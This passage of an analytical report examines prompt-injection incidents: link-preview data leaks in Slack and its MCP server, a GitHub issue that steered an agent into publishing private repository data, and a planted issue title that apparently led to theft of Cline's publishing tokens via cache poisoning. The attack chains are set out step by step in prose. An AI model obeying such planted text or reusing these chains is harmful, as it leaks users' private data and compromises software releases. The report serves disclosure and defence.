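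Slack did not identify the model that answered in the demonstration either, though Anthropic probably supplied it. In a May 2026 engineering post, Slack said it had hosted Anthropic's models on Amazon SageMaker before it began moving to Amazon Bedrock in mid-2024. Under the SageMaker arrangement, Anthropic could not see Slack's data and so could not notice such an attack in customers' prompts. Slack could not retrain the model against the attack because it had no access to the weights, the numbers that determine the model's behavior. A patch that Slack shipped within a day almost certainly changed the application around the model.

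Since early 2026 Slack has also used models on Google's cloud. Its software sends each request to whichever model suits the feature and switches automatically when one slows down or returns errors. Slack checks new models for security and compliance before using them, but a switch may still change how well the assistant resists planted text, as with the fallback model in Claude Cowork.

### When the app opens the link itself

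When someone pastes a link into a chat, many messaging apps fetch the page to show its title and a picture. Developers call this unfurling. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* says, "When a link is spotted, Slack crawls it and provides a preview." The feature was harmless enough while people wrote the links, because people rarely put secrets in web addresses.

An AI agent that has read planted text might post a link with private data at the end. The preview request then carries that data to the attacker's server, as image requests did in ChatGPT and Bing Chat. The data leaves as soon as the message is posted, even if nobody reads it. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* includes a log entry from Rehberger's test, in which the visitor identified itself as "Slackbot-LinkExpanding". The request came from Slack's servers, so a content security policy didn't help,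 just as it didn't with ChatGPT's Deep Research.

On August 21, the day of Slack's statement about Slack AI, Willison (2024) admitted in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* that he had not thought of this route before, although he had been collecting such leaks for more than a year.

Slack already let developers turn off previews for links and media by adding two settings to each message a bot posts, but it described the default inconsistently. Rehberger quoted Slack's documentation as saying that Slack previews all links in messages from users and apps unless told otherwise. According to Slack's reference page for the posting function, links to media get a preview by default and links to text pages do not, except inside structured sections called blocks. A developer who read only the reference page could reasonably conclude that an ordinary link was safe. In Rehberger's test,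 which posted a plain link by a method other than that function, Slack fetched the link.

### A server that nobody maintains

When Anthropic introduced MCP, it published several example servers, including one that let an AI agent read and post Slack messages. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* (2025) reports that this server left link previews on. Rehberger reported this to Anthropic on May 27, 2025. Anthropic archived the server two days later, but he could not tell whether the two were connected.

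In one of his demonstrations, a developer asks Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to analyze a source code file that contains instructions written in invisible characters. The agent follows them, opening a settings file where developers often keep keys and posting a link containing a key to Slack. Slack's preview programs then deliver the key to the attacker. In another, a user of Anthropic's desktop app asks the agent to summarize a document and post the summary for the team. The document contains instructions to take the latest message from one Slack channel and post it, as part of a link, in a different, private channel.

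The private channel matters because the server's settings let an administrator limit posting to particular channels. Most AI applications ask the user before each use of a tool, but people tire of approving harmless actions, and letting an agent post unsupervised to a single private channel looks harmless because only colleagues can see the messages. With previews on, any data in a message's links also goes to whoever owns the linked address. The restriction did limit where the agent could post, but it misled users about where their data could go.

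Anthropic told Rehberger that it was comfortable with publication, and he did not expect it to issue a CVE. VulnCheck, a security firm authorized to assign CVEs, issued one instead. NIST's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025) gives a publication date of July 2, 2025, and VulnCheck's severity score of 9.3, but no score from NIST itself. Rehberger had scored the vulnerability 7.5. VulnCheck's score may be higher partly because it also counts serious damage to the integrity and availability of other systems, which his demonstrations did not include. VulnCheck's *Anthropic Slack MCP Server Data Exfiltration via Link Unfurling* lists every default installation as affected.

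Anthropic never patched the flaw. Snyk's *Improper Neutralization of Input Used for LLM Prompting* (2025), an entry in a commercial vulnerability database, confirms that no fixed version exists. The notice on the archive, reproduced in Glama's *Model Context Protocol servers (ARCHIVED)*, says there will be no security updates and tells people to use the servers at their own risk. Anthropic's reason for not fixing the flaw was therefore that it had stopped maintaining the program, and Rehberger mentions no dispute over whether the flaw was real. His own fix adds Slack's two settings wherever the server posts or replies. It stopped the previews in his test, but every user has to apply it to their own copy.

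Rehberger counted more than 14,000 weekly downloads of the server in 2025. npm's *Slack MCP Server*, the package's page in the registry where developers get it, marks it as unsupported but shows 19,728 weekly downloads in a later count. Automated systems may download the same package many times, so neither figure is the number of users. The software company Zencoder has published its own version of the server. Zencoder's *slack-mcp-server* lists newer protocol software and better error handling among its changes, but no change to previews. The fix takes only two extra lines, which could easily go unlisted, so this doesn't prove that Zencoder's version leaks.

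### Which pairs leaked

In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* invited the public to test other combinations. Visitors got their own agent to post a link to a test website, which logged any preview request and the data in it. They could then "claim" their log entry and name the agent and the app they had used. They could also report combinations that produced no request. Intelligibberish's *Link Previews Are Leaking Your Data to AI Agents Without a Click* lists the results:

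| Messaging app | Agents whose links the app fetched | Agents reported as safer |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Teams | Copilot Studio | None listed |
| Slack | Cursor's Slackbot | Claude app |
| Discord | OpenClaw, BoltBot | None listed |
| Telegram | OpenClaw | None listed |
| Snapchat | SnapAI | None listed |
| WhatsApp | None listed | OpenClaw |
| Signal | None listed | OpenClaw running in Docker |

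Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building assistants, accounted for the largest share of the requests from Teams and the other apps. That share reflects who took part as much as how risky the product is, and PromptArmor relied on visitors to name their software correctly. The test also covered only the last step of an attack, in which an app fetches a link an agent has written. It did not test how easily planted text could get the agent to write one.

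Even with those limits, the results suggest that link fetching depended on both the agent and the messaging app. Telegram and Discord fetched links from OpenClaw, an agent that people run themselves and talk to through chat apps, but WhatsApp did not. Slack fetched links from Cursor's bot but not from Anthropic's Claude app. A customer who tested an agent in one messaging app, or a messaging app with one agent, would therefore have learned little about other combinations.

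### Who should turn the preview off

PromptArmor said that messaging apps should give developers control over link previews, ideally for each chat or channel, and that agent developers should use that control or pass the choice to their users. Apostol's trade report on the research, *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, put the responsibility largely on the messaging platforms, a stronger position than PromptArmor's own.

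In Slack's case, the bot's developer is better placed than Slack to turn off link previews, because the developer knows that a model wrote the message, while Slack's software treats the bot like any other app posting a link. Developers can already turn previews off with two lines of code. Rehberger recommends that any AI tool posting to a messaging app have previews off unless someone deliberately turns them on, which would take developers little work and close this attack route for all their customers. OpenClaw had such a setting for Telegram when PromptArmor tested it, but previews were on by default, and users had to edit a configuration file to turn them off.

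This division fails for the archived server, which no longer has a developer who will act. Slack could protect every copy at once by previewing links only from apps that ask for it. Many ordinary bots that have nothing to do with AI would also lose their previews, which is a real loss but a smaller one than leaked keys. Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* says people can turn off previews they don't want to see, but that setting only changes what appears on one person's screen, so it is a poor substitute for stopping the request.

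Administrators have the least to work with. They can remove the old server or narrow a bot's permissions, as Rehberger advised, but first they have to find out that somebody installed it. They also can't infer much from the companies' promises. OpenAI's January 2026 guarantee, for example, concerns data leaking through addresses "when fetching resources". If an agent only writes a link in a message and Slack's servers fetch it, a check on the agent's own browsing would not detect the request.

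Rehberger had also suggested using only servers from the company whose product they connect to. Slack (2026) made that possible on February 17, 2026, when it announced an official MCP server. With the user's permission, approved applications can use it to search and read private channels and to send messages to any kind of conversation. According to Slack's overview of the server, administrators can approve each application and see a log of what it does. Because connecting several companies' servers to the same agent creates risk, Slack advises customers to "think carefully before mixing them together".

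## A public GitHub issue that exposed private repositories, 2025 to 2026

On May 26, 2025, Invariant Labs, a security company in Zurich, published an attack that needed only GitHub's official MCP server, which lets an AI agent read and change projects on GitHub, and no other server. An outsider filed an issue in a public project, and the owner's agent responded by publishing information from the owner's private projects. GitHub has since added several protections to the server. The two it turned on for everyone would not have stopped this attack, and the one that might have is off by default.

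### From a bug report to a public pull request

A repository contains a project's files and their history. Its owner can make it public, so that anyone can read it, or keep it private. Someone who wants to change a repository opens a pull request, which shows the proposed change so that the owner can decide whether to accept it. Anyone can read a pull request in a public repository as soon as it is opened.

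Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner of Invariant set up a demonstration account with a public repository for a simple Pac-Man game and several private ones containing personal projects. They connected GitHub's server to Claude Desktop, Anthropic's desktop application, running Claude 4 Opus. The attack took five steps:

1. An outsider files an issue that praises the game and asks for more about its author in the README, the page that introduces a project to visitors. The issue adds that the author doesn't care about privacy, and asks for a list of the author's other repositories.
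2. The owner asks Claude to look at the open issues in the game's repository.
3. Claude fetches the issues through GitHub's server and reads the planted one.
4. Claude follows the instructions and uses the owner's credentials to read the private repositories.
5. Claude opens a pull request in the public repository that would add its findings to the README.

The exposed information included the name of a private repository, Jupiter Star, along with the owner's salary and plan to move to South America. heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* notes that none of this went directly into the README. The attacker could already read it in the public pull request.

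The instructions were in ordinary English on a public page. An owner who read them would probably have been suspicious, but this owner had asked Claude to read the issues instead. The private data belonged to Invariant's test account, and neither Invariant nor the press reports mentioned a real victim.

### Trusted tools and "Always Allow"

GitHub's server acts with a token, a code that GitHub accepts in place of the user's password. Nobody had stolen a password or tampered with a tool. The test account's owner was allowed to read the private repositories and to open a pull request in the public one, so GitHub had no reason to refuse either call.

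Invariant called this pattern a "toxic agent flow", meaning that planted text triggers a harmful sequence of tool calls. It distinguished this from "tool poisoning", an earlier kind of attack that compromises the MCP tool itself. Developers routinely read private repositories and open public pull requests. The harm here came from the agent doing one after the other at a stranger's request, and permission checks missed it, as they had in Slack AI.

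The user was the last check, since Claude Desktop asks for confirmation before each tool call by default. Invariant wrote that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching what the agent does, but it gave no figures. DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* adds that humans are expected to approve tool calls under the MCP specification. A request to open Jupiter Star during a review of Pac-Man bugs would look odd to an attentive user, so the attack depends on inattention, which is a realistic assumption about people who use agents all day.

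"Always Allow" also applies to a tool regardless of what data the agent has read. A developer might grant it when the agent proposes a spelling correction, and it would still apply weeks later when a proposed change contains a salary.

### Whose problem it was

Invariant announced "a critical vulnerability" with GitHub's server, but said later in the announcement that the server's code was not at fault. It called the problem architectural and said that "GitHub alone cannot resolve this vulnerability through server-side patches." It didn't expect model providers to solve the problem either. Claude 4 Opus had followed a fairly simple injection despite its safety training, and Invariant argued that training can't anticipate what each organization needs to protect. It also said that many off-the-shelf injection detectors missed the attack.

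That left the agent system, the application that combines the model with its tools and permissions. Invariant sells controls for that layer. It recommended its Guardrails product, which applies rules to an agent's tool calls, and its MCP-scan product, which monitors the traffic between agents and servers. It ended by inviting readers to contact the company. Invariant also said that the attack affected any agent using GitHub's server, regardless of the model, though its experiments focused on Claude Desktop. Newer models are much harder to hijack, so the same GitHub issue would probably succeed less often today.

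flyingpenguin's *RBAC in a Bunny Costume*, a blog post attacking the disclosure, argued that there was no vulnerability at all. The user had given an agent access to everything and then turned off or ignored the confirmations. GitHub had for years offered tokens limited to chosen repositories, and a token limited to the Pac-Man repository would have made the private ones unreachable. On this view, Invariant had presented a bad configuration as a critical flaw in order to sell monitoring software.

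The post's remedy is right for this user, who needed only the game's issues. A narrow token is free and works even if the model obeys the planted text. But it doesn't help someone who works with both private and public repositories, because a token that covers both allows the same leak. Invariant had also recommended limiting an agent's access to the repositories it needs, but objected that tokens are often too rigid. The two sides disagree mainly about how many people can work with a narrow token, and neither offered evidence on that.

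### One repository per session

Invariant's alternative to narrow tokens was a rule that limits an agent to one repository per session. Guardrails compares each repository action with earlier ones and blocks the call if the repository's name or owner has changed. In the demonstration, Claude had already listed the Pac-Man issues, so the rule would have blocked its first attempt to read Jupiter Star. The rule runs outside the model, so text in an issue cannot override it.

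Under this rule, a developer could no longer ask an agent to copy a fix from one project to another, or to check whether a change in a shared library breaks the programs that depend on it. Each repository would need its own session, and the developer would have to carry information between sessions. The rule would also block harmless work, such as moving between two public repositories that contain no private data.

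It also leaves some leaks open. Documentation that GitHub later wrote for the server explains that some information is private even when the repository is public. For example, a secret scanning alert, which warns maintainers that a password or key has ended up in their code, can include the secret itself. An agent with access to those alerts could publish one without leaving the repository. This would affect only people who had added the alert tools, because GitHub doesn't include them in the server's default set. The documentation also describes searches that return results from several repositories in one call. A rule that compares the repository named in each call would need to handle those searches separately.

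### What GitHub and Anthropic said

The reports in DevClass and heise online contain no comment from either company. Herkos' *Exfil through an approved tool*, a case note by the maker of a tool that logs agents' actions, found no CVE and no response from GitHub. It adds that a community member reported a reproduction of the attack to the server's project in August 2025, and that the report went stale without an official reply.

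The closest thing to a statement of GitHub's position came from SamMorrowDrums, a maintainer of the server, who proposed in *Invisible character filtering* to remove hidden text from issues and comments before an agent reads them. The maintainer wrote that this "doesn't prevent such attacks". It would only make them visible, so that a user who checks the agent's actions could see what had gone wrong and stop it. Applications that run agents without such checks should treat everything an MCP server returns as potentially hostile. This position left the application and its user responsible for preventing attacks.

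Anthropic's current guidance doesn't mention Invariant's attack. Anthropic's *Get started with custom connectors using remote MCP* tells users to click "Allow always" only for "a server and tool that you trust to run unsupervised". Its warning about prompt injection covers malicious servers that include hidden instructions, but GitHub's server was trustworthy and accurately delivered a stranger's text. A user who read the warning could reasonably conclude that an official server was safe to run unsupervised.

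Another Anthropic page more usefully explains how to limit GitHub's server to read-only access, which would have stopped the original attack at the pull request. Anthropic only requires users to sign in to GitHub to connect to the server's ordinary address, but to use the read-only address, they must first register an app with GitHub and enter its ID and secret. A simpler method, adding a setting to each request, is in beta for a limited set of organizations. Users can also connect the server and then block the tools that write to GitHub, but each user must do this individually.

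Giving an agent read-only access helps only if no other component can publish on its behalf. In July 2026, the security company Noma demonstrated a similar leak, GitLost, in GitHub's own service for running agents in build pipelines. According to mcp.directory's *GitLost*, the GitHub server in that test was read-only, but a separate component posted the private text as a public comment.

### Secret scanning and hidden text

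In August 2025, GitHub began scanning the tool calls that agents make to public repositories through its hosted version of the server. If a call contains a secret, such as a password or access key, the server blocks it and explains why, but the user can override the block. GitHub presented this as protection against planted text that tricks an agent into publishing credentials. According to GitHub's documentation, the protection is on by default for all public repositories, whatever their security settings.

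The scan would not have stopped Invariant's attack. A scanner can recognize an access key by its format, but a salary or a plan to move abroad has no standard format. GitHub acknowledged in the announcement that the feature doesn't stop leaks of non-secret data. If one of the private repositories had contained an access key, the scan might well have blocked the pull request.

In December 2025, GitHub set its server to remove hidden text, much as the server's maintainer had proposed. The server now strips invisible characters, unsafe HTML and text concealed in code blocks. In GitHub's example, a code block contains a hidden request for a list of the user's private repositories, and the server passes on only the visible line of code. The request resembles Invariant's, but Invariant had not hidden anything, so its issue would have gone through unchanged.

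Removing hidden text is still worthwhile because a maintainer who reads an issue before handing it to an agent can now be more confident that both see the same words. That benefit depends on the maintainer reading the issue first, which the original victim was using an agent to avoid. The announcement also listed comments among the places where attackers hide text but promised cleaning only for "issues and pull requests", so it was unclear whether comments were covered.

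### Lockdown mode

The same December release added an optional lockdown mode. When it is on, the server hides from the agent any text in public repositories, including issues, written by someone without push access (permission to change the repository's files directly). Someone had already suggested a similar filter to the project when DevClass reported Invariant's attack in May. DevClass called the idea interesting but crude, because it would probably exclude many useful contributions.

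Lockdown mode would have stopped the original attack if the owner had turned it on and Claude had opened the planted issue with a tool the mode covers. GitHub's list of covered tools includes those that read a single issue, its comments, or a pull request, but not the tool that lists a repository's issues. According to Herkos, the listing tool was the one that returned the planted text in full. GitHub's documentation for its pipeline service describes the mode more broadly, as showing only items from people with push access. If the narrower list is accurate, the planted text could have reached Claude even with lockdown mode on.

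The mode also prevents the agent from doing much of what people want from it. The pipeline documentation recommends turning it off for sorting issues, detecting spam and planning work based on issues, because those jobs require reading what strangers write. Invariant's hypothetical owner had asked Claude to look at the open issues. If the mode had been fully effective, Claude would have seen only the issues filed by people with push access, which in a popular project would leave out most of the bug reports.

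Lockdown mode nevertheless shows that a change to the server can interrupt this kind of attack, so Invariant's verdict was too sweeping. GitHub could have gone further by enforcing Invariant's one-repository rule on its server, provided the server tracked which calls belonged to the same session. Every call in the demonstration went through that server, and the rule needs only the repository names in those calls.

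Invariant was right about the wider problem. GitHub's server can't protect an agent that takes private data from the user's own computer or publishes through another company's server. It also can't determine whether the owner or a stranger prompted a request to read Jupiter Star. No fix to the server's code would let an agent read strangers' issues, use private repositories and write in public without risking a leak. GitHub could choose which of those abilities to restrict, but it left that choice to users.

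### Corrections to lockdown mode in 2026

Lockdown mode decides whether to show an issue by checking whether the issue's author has push access on GitHub. On a server shared by several people, it should make this check with the current user's credentials. OSV's *CVE-2026-48529* (2026), an entry in a database of flaws in open-source software, records that lockdown mode used the first user's credentials for everyone who signed in later. Docker Scout's *CVE-2026-48529* explains that the server relied on these checks in at least six places to decide whether to trust an outsider's text. The information GitHub returns about a repository depends on whose credentials are used, so the server could have made the wrong decision.

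The flaw affected versions from 0.22.0 until the fix in 1.1.2 and has a CVSS score of 6.0. Someone running the server alone had no other user's credentials to confuse with their own. GitHub itself assigned this CVE, but Invariant's attack never received one. A vulnerability scanner could therefore report the flaw in the optional protection but not the leak that the protection was meant to prevent.

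Aikido, which sells vulnerability scanning, lists an earlier fault that GitHub fixed in version 1.0.3. Aikido rates the risk as high and says the permission checks could have let malicious users get their text past the filter, but it doesn't demonstrate such a bypass. Its entry wrongly marks every version from 0.0.1 as affected, since the filter was still only a proposal when the server was at version 0.4.0.

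Classmethod's *Reducing Prompt Injection Risk with GitHub MCP Lockdown Mode* (2026), a hands-on test from August 2026, found that lockdown mode blocked too much. The tester used issues in the GitHub server's own public repository, where they had no push access. The server returned an outsider's issue in full with the mode off, but returned an error with it on. The tester got the same error for an issue whose author probably did have push access. GitHub did not let the tester, as an outsider, see who held which permissions, and the server withheld any issue whose author's access it could not check.

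That is the safer way for a check to fail, but it makes the mode nearly useless to developers researching other people's projects. They have to turn it off for the repositories whose contributors they know least.

Users must still turn on lockdown and read-only modes, according to the instructions GitHub (2026) published with version 1.4.0 in June. Without these settings, an agent gets tools for repositories, issues and pull requests, which together cover every step of Invariant's attack. GitHub advises users to give tokens only the necessary permissions and to keep separate tokens for different projects. Users who follow this advice get much of the benefit of the one-repository rule without buying anything.

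### Labels that follow the data

About a year after the disclosure, Microsoft's *Information-flow control* revisited this attack and described a defense Microsoft had built with GitHub. The server labels the text it returns as trusted or untrusted, and as public or private. The application running the agent tracks these labels, and anything the agent produces takes on the most restrictive labels of the material it has read.

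In Invariant's attack, Claude's session would have been marked untrusted when Claude read the planted issue and private when it read the other repositories. A rule in the application would then have stopped it from posting anything in public, or asked the user first. Because the application enforces the rule, it works even if the planted text manipulates the model. The agent could still work across several public repositories, or several private ones, which the one-repository rule forbids. Users also have more reason to read a confirmation if it appears only when private data is about to become public.

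The protection depends on accurate labels, and the two companies describe one of them differently. According to Microsoft's article, issues from private repositories count as trusted. GitHub's *ifc* (2026), the documentation for the labels as of May, says that the text of an issue is always untrusted because an attacker could have written it. GitHub's choice is safer because even a private repository can have a contractor or a compromised account among its members, and under Microsoft's version an issue from either could direct an agent to publish private material.

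Users have to request the labels, and the server doesn't enforce them. GitHub's documentation says enforcement "lives in a separate service". Microsoft had added support for the labels to its own framework for building agents and, experimentally, to GitHub's command-line agent. The experimental support covered only some of the GitHub server's tools and no other company's servers. Applications that don't understand the labels work as before. Microsoft's article doesn't mention support in Claude Desktop, the application Invariant used.

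## The theft of Cline's publishing credentials, February 2026

Eight months after Invariant's demonstration, someone attacked a real project through a GitHub issue. Cline is an open-source coding assistant with more than five million installs, and its maintainers used an AI agent to answer new issues. On February 17, 2026, an attacker published an altered version of Cline's command-line program that installed a second AI agent on users' computers without asking them. The attacker used a stolen publishing token that Cline believed it had revoked. The evidence that the theft began with the issue agent is strong but incomplete.

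### An agent that answered strangers

On December 21, 2025, Cline's maintainers added a GitHub Actions job that ran Claude whenever someone opened an issue. They built it with claude-code-action, Anthropic's ready-made component for running its coding agent on GitHub. The agent was supposed to write the first response to each issue and save the maintainers time.

The security researcher Adnan Khan found the flaw within days. His *Clinejection* (2026) explains that the maintainers had set the job to run for anyone with a GitHub account and had given the agent tools for editing files, browsing the web and running commands. The job also copied the issue's title into the prompt, so an attacker could write a title that resembled an error message and told the agent to install a helper program before continuing. The installer would run the attacker's code immediately, giving the model no chance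 to inspect it. Khan tested this on a copy of Cline's repository, and Claude Opus 4.5 followed the instruction in every attempt.

The job did not look especially dangerous. Cline had restricted the permissions of the job's GitHub token, and the only secret the agent could reach directly was the key for using Anthropic's models. The tokens for publishing Cline were in other jobs.

### From the issue job to the release job

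Build pipelines keep a cache of files, such as software libraries, so that each job doesn't have to download them again. On GitHub, all jobs running on a project's main branch could read and write the same cache, even if nobody had set them up to use it. Khan described an attack that used this shared storage to get from one job to the other:

1. The attacker opens an issue whose title makes the agent run the attacker's code.
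2. That code fills the cache with junk until GitHub deletes the genuine files to make room.
3. The code saves altered files under the names of the deleted ones.
4. At about 2 a.m. UTC, the job that publishes Cline's nightly test version loads the altered files. The code in them runs inside that job and sends its publishing tokens to the attacker.

The second step is necessary because a job can't overwrite a file that is already in the cache. GitHub had unintentionally made this step easier. It used to check once a day whether a project had exceeded its 10 GB limit, but its *New date for enforcement of cache eviction policy* (2025) announced hourly checks from November. Khan says deletion actually became immediate, so an attacker could make the whole swap in a few minutes.

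Cline's production release job did not use the cache, but the nightly job's tokens could publish production versions too. The VS Code Marketplace and Open VSX, which distribute Cline's extension for code editors, tie a token to a publisher rather than to a single extension, and Cline published its test and production extensions under the same identity. npm, the registry that distributes the command-line program, can limit a token to one package, but Cline used the same package for both kinds of release. Khan recommended a separate package and publishing account for test versions.

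### Five weeks without a reply

Khan reported the flaw on January 1, 2026, through GitHub's private reporting system and by email to Cline's security address. He emailed a developer on January 8, messaged Cline's chief executive on January 18, and wrote to the security address again on February 7. He received only a ticket number. He made the flaw public on February 9, and Cline removed the agent about half an hour later.

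By then someone else had tried the attack. Bargury (2026), in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, recovered a deleted issue from a public archive of GitHub activity. An account called "glthub-actions", with a lowercase L in place of the "i" in "github", had opened it on Cline's repository on January 28. The title contained an instruction for the agent to install a helper program, in wording close to Khan's. About five minutes later the issue was closed, with its title changed to "user error".

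Khan had not yet published anything, but he had tested the attack in a public copy of Cline's repository, where anyone could read his trial issues. He confirmed to Bargury that this copy had been public "until recently". Bargury concluded that the attacker had probably found the method by watching Khan's activity on GitHub.

Khan's blog post is hard to blame for the theft because the attack came 12 days before it. The attack also came 27 days after his first report, so a prompt reply from Cline would probably have prevented it. Khan's choice of a public test repository is easier to criticize. He was careful to avoid testing on Cline's own systems, but a private copy would have kept the method hidden while he waited.

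### What ties the theft to the issue

Cline has confirmed that the attacker published with a compromised npm token, which it called the "exposed" token in a message to Khan. The recovered issue shows that someone attempted the prompt injection on the real project. Khan noticed unusual failures in Cline's nightly release jobs between January 31 and February 3. They matched the traces left by a publicly available tool he had written to demonstrate cache attacks. On February 10, an anonymous emailer told him that they had working npm and Open VSX credentials for Cline.

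Together, these make the route Khan described by far the most likely. But no published account includes a log of the agent running the command on January 28 or of the token leaving the release job. Bargury found that the script named in the attacker's code had been deleted. SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised* cautions that nobody has publicly confirmed exactly how the attacker stole the token, but Snyk's *How “Clinejection” Turned an AI Bot into a Supply Chain Attack* (2026) treats the February release as an exploitation of the same flaw. Snyk discloses a security partnership with Cline.

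The attacker's identity is less certain than the method. Bargury is highly confident that the person behind the account "glthub-actions" stole the credentials and published the altered version. He thinks this person was a bug hunter making a demonstration, because the account had tried a different attack the day before on a test project that New Relic had set up for bug hunters. That would explain the harmless payload, but the people whose computers were affected had not agreed to a demonstration. The Hacker News (2026) reported that it was not clear who had done it or why.

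### The token that stayed valid

After Khan's post, Cline removed the issue agent, stopped its release jobs from using the cache and replaced its credentials. Khan forwarded the anonymous warning on February 10. The next day Cline replied that it had revoked all earlier publishing tokens. It had also compared every release since December 21 with its source code and found no unauthorized versions, so it told Khan that users didn't need to do anything.

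Cline seems to have been right about the releases, but it was wrong about the tokens. On February 17 it wrote to Khan again: "The wrong token was deleted, and the exposed one remained active." Comparing old releases could show whether an attacker had used a token, but not whether the token still worked. Cline would have had to check the exposed token to find that out, and it had a specific warning that this token might still be valid.

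OSV's *Unauthorized npm publish of cline@2.3.0 with modified postinstall script* (2026) reproduces Cline's advisory. The attacker published version 2.3.0 at 3:26 a.m. Pacific time on February 17. This version was identical to the previous one except for an instruction to install the AI agent OpenClaw. Cline released a clean version at 11:23 a.m. and marked the altered one as deprecated seven minutes later.

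StepSecurity, which sells monitoring of software releases, had flagged the altered version within 14 minutes. The company's account, *Cline Supply Chain Attack Detected* (Likhith, 2026), puts downloads at about 4,000, which fits the package's usual traffic of roughly 420,000 a month. The number of people affected may be lower. The Hacker News reports that Microsoft's threat researchers saw a "small but noticeable uptick" in OpenClaw installations that day, so the altered version did reach real machines.

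The security companies disagree about how serious this was. Likhith warned that OpenClaw runs a permanent background service with wide access to the computer, which would give an attacker a lasting foothold. Plate (2026), in *Supply Chain Attack targeting Cline installs OpenClaw*, said the altered version never installed or started that service, and rated the impact low. Plate, whose employer Endor Labs also sells software security, thought it was more like a prank than a serious attack. The published instruction supports Plate's reading, since it only installed the package.

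Cline's advisory also rates the incident low, while Snyk's *Malicious Package Affecting cline package, versions =2.3.0* (2026) rates the package critical. The low rating fits the damage done but understates the danger, because whoever controlled that token could have put a password stealer in the package. With a working token for the editor extension, they could have reached far more people, many of whom had automatic updates turned on.

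### What Cline accepted and changed

The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1680* lists a public post-mortem from Cline and records that the company found no evidence of exposed user data. In messages to Khan, Cline agreed that the design of its issue-sorting job "required hardening" and called its response time to his first report "unacceptable". After the altered release, it conceded that he had been right to question whether it had replaced all its credentials. It promised to handle security reports faster and to put stricter limits on any future agent that sorted issues.

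Cline initially pointed out that a maintainer had to approve each production release, which it said had reduced the exposure. The approval was part of Cline's release process, which anyone with a valid npm token could skip by uploading a version directly, as the attacker did.

The advisory says that Cline now publishes to npm through GitHub Actions with OpenID Connect, which uses short-lived credentials tied to the project's pipeline, so there is no permanent token to steal. But Likhith found that earlier legitimate releases had already used this method. Plate concluded that Cline had turned it on without turning off token-based publishing, which npm's documentation strongly recommended restricting. If Cline had followed that advice, the forgotten token would have been useless.

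The new method would not help if an attacker's code were running in the release job, because that code could publish while the job's credentials were valid. Removing the cache from release jobs was therefore at least as important.

### Anthropic's warning and its example

Anthropic supplied both the model that followed the title's instructions in Khan's tests and claude-code-action, the component that ran it. By default, claude-code-action responds only to people with write access to the repository, but Cline had used a setting that removes this restriction. Anthropic's *Security* (2025) marked the setting "RISKY" in November, a month before Cline installed the agent. Anthropic could fairly say that Cline had ignored its advice by turning off a protection.

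That defense is weaker than it looks, because Anthropic had ignored part of its own advice. RyotaK, a researcher at the security testing company GMO Flatt Security, reports in *Poisoning Claude Code* (2026) that Anthropic's example for sorting issues used the same setting and let any GitHub user start the agent. According to a comment in the example, the job needed this so that people without write access could file issues. RyotaK found that many projects had inherited the weakness from the example. None of the accounts identifies Cline as one of them, and Cline had also given its agent far more tools than it needed for sorting issues.

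The warning was also incomplete. It said to use the setting only in jobs with "extremely limited permissions", such as one that could only write to issues. Cline had limited its job's GitHub permissions, but every job on the main branch could access the cache regardless of how its token was restricted. A maintainer who followed the warning could still have left this route open if the agent could run commands.

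RyotaK reported the unsafe example to Anthropic on January 17, eleven days before the attack on Cline. Anthropic made several rounds of fixes between February and April, including no longer publishing a summary of the agent's work by default and removing secrets from the environment of programs the agent starts. Microsoft (2026) found that the agent could still read secrets through its file-reading tool. This was one of several flaws found in vendors' GitHub agents, and Anthropic fixed it on May 5, six days after the report.

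These fixes mainly protect secrets within the agent's own job. In the attack Khan described, the attacker used the cache to reach valuable secrets in another job, so removing secrets from the first job might not have prevented the theft. RyotaK still advises against letting strangers start the agent. That advice matters beyond Cline. Wiz's *The (In)security Landscape of AI-Powered GitHub Actions (Part 2/2)* counted more than 12,000 public workflows that use Anthropic's component, though most may have kept the default restriction.

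### Changes to the cache and the registries

GitHub knew that attackers could use the cache this way. The documentation for its code scanner describes how code in a low-privilege job can plant files that a more privileged job later runs. The scanner could warn a project of the danger, but the shared cache stayed writable by default.

GitHub's *Read-only Actions cache for untrusted triggers* (2026) announced on June 26 that jobs that run on the main branch and can be triggered by an outsider can now read the shared cache but not write to it. This includes an agent that starts when a stranger opens an issue, so the new rule would have blocked the attack at the second step. It applies to every project automatically. A few legitimate jobs can no longer save files to the cache, but they still run and can use files that trusted jobs have saved.

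The change came more than four months after the altered release, and Cline may not have been the reason. The announcement doesn't mention Cline, and when GitHub (2026) set out its security plans in March, it cited attacks on three other projects. Still, GitHub cut the connection between the two jobs without solving prompt injection or requiring thousands of maintainers to change their settings.

GitHub also runs npm, and has made changes there that would have affected the last part of the attack. In May, it introduced staged publishing, which holds a new version until a person approves it with a second form of authentication. If maintainers turn this on, a stolen token is no longer enough to publish a version.

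Version 12 of npm's installation program blocks two things by default. One is installation scripts, which the altered Cline release used to install OpenClaw. The other is packages fetched directly from a code repository, and the agent was instructed in the planted issue to get its helper program that way. An attacker could have told the agent to run a different command, so these defaults protect Cline's users better than they protect a job that lets strangers direct an agent.

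GitHub's changes to npm don't affect tokens at the VS Code Marketplace and Open VSX, where one token covers all of a publisher's releases. Maintainers can separate test and production releases by publishing them under different identities, as Khan recommended, but they have to know that the tokens are shared.

### Whether Cline's settings explain the theft

Cline deserves most of the blame. It let strangers direct an agent that could run commands, and it kept tokens that could publish production versions in a nightly job that loaded files from a shared cache. It then missed Khan's reports for more than five weeks and failed to revoke the token after being warned. Correcting any one of these mistakes would probably have prevented the February release. Daelman's *PromptPwnd* had publicly described the general pattern in several vendors' agents, and Khan says that work covered Cline's exact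 misconfiguration.

But Cline's settings explain only how a stranger could control the issue agent. That control led to the publishing tokens only because GitHub let a job with few permissions change files that a trusted job would later run. Anthropic's example also made it look normal to open such an agent to everyone. A small team could read the warning, restrict the job's token and reasonably believe it had contained the risk.

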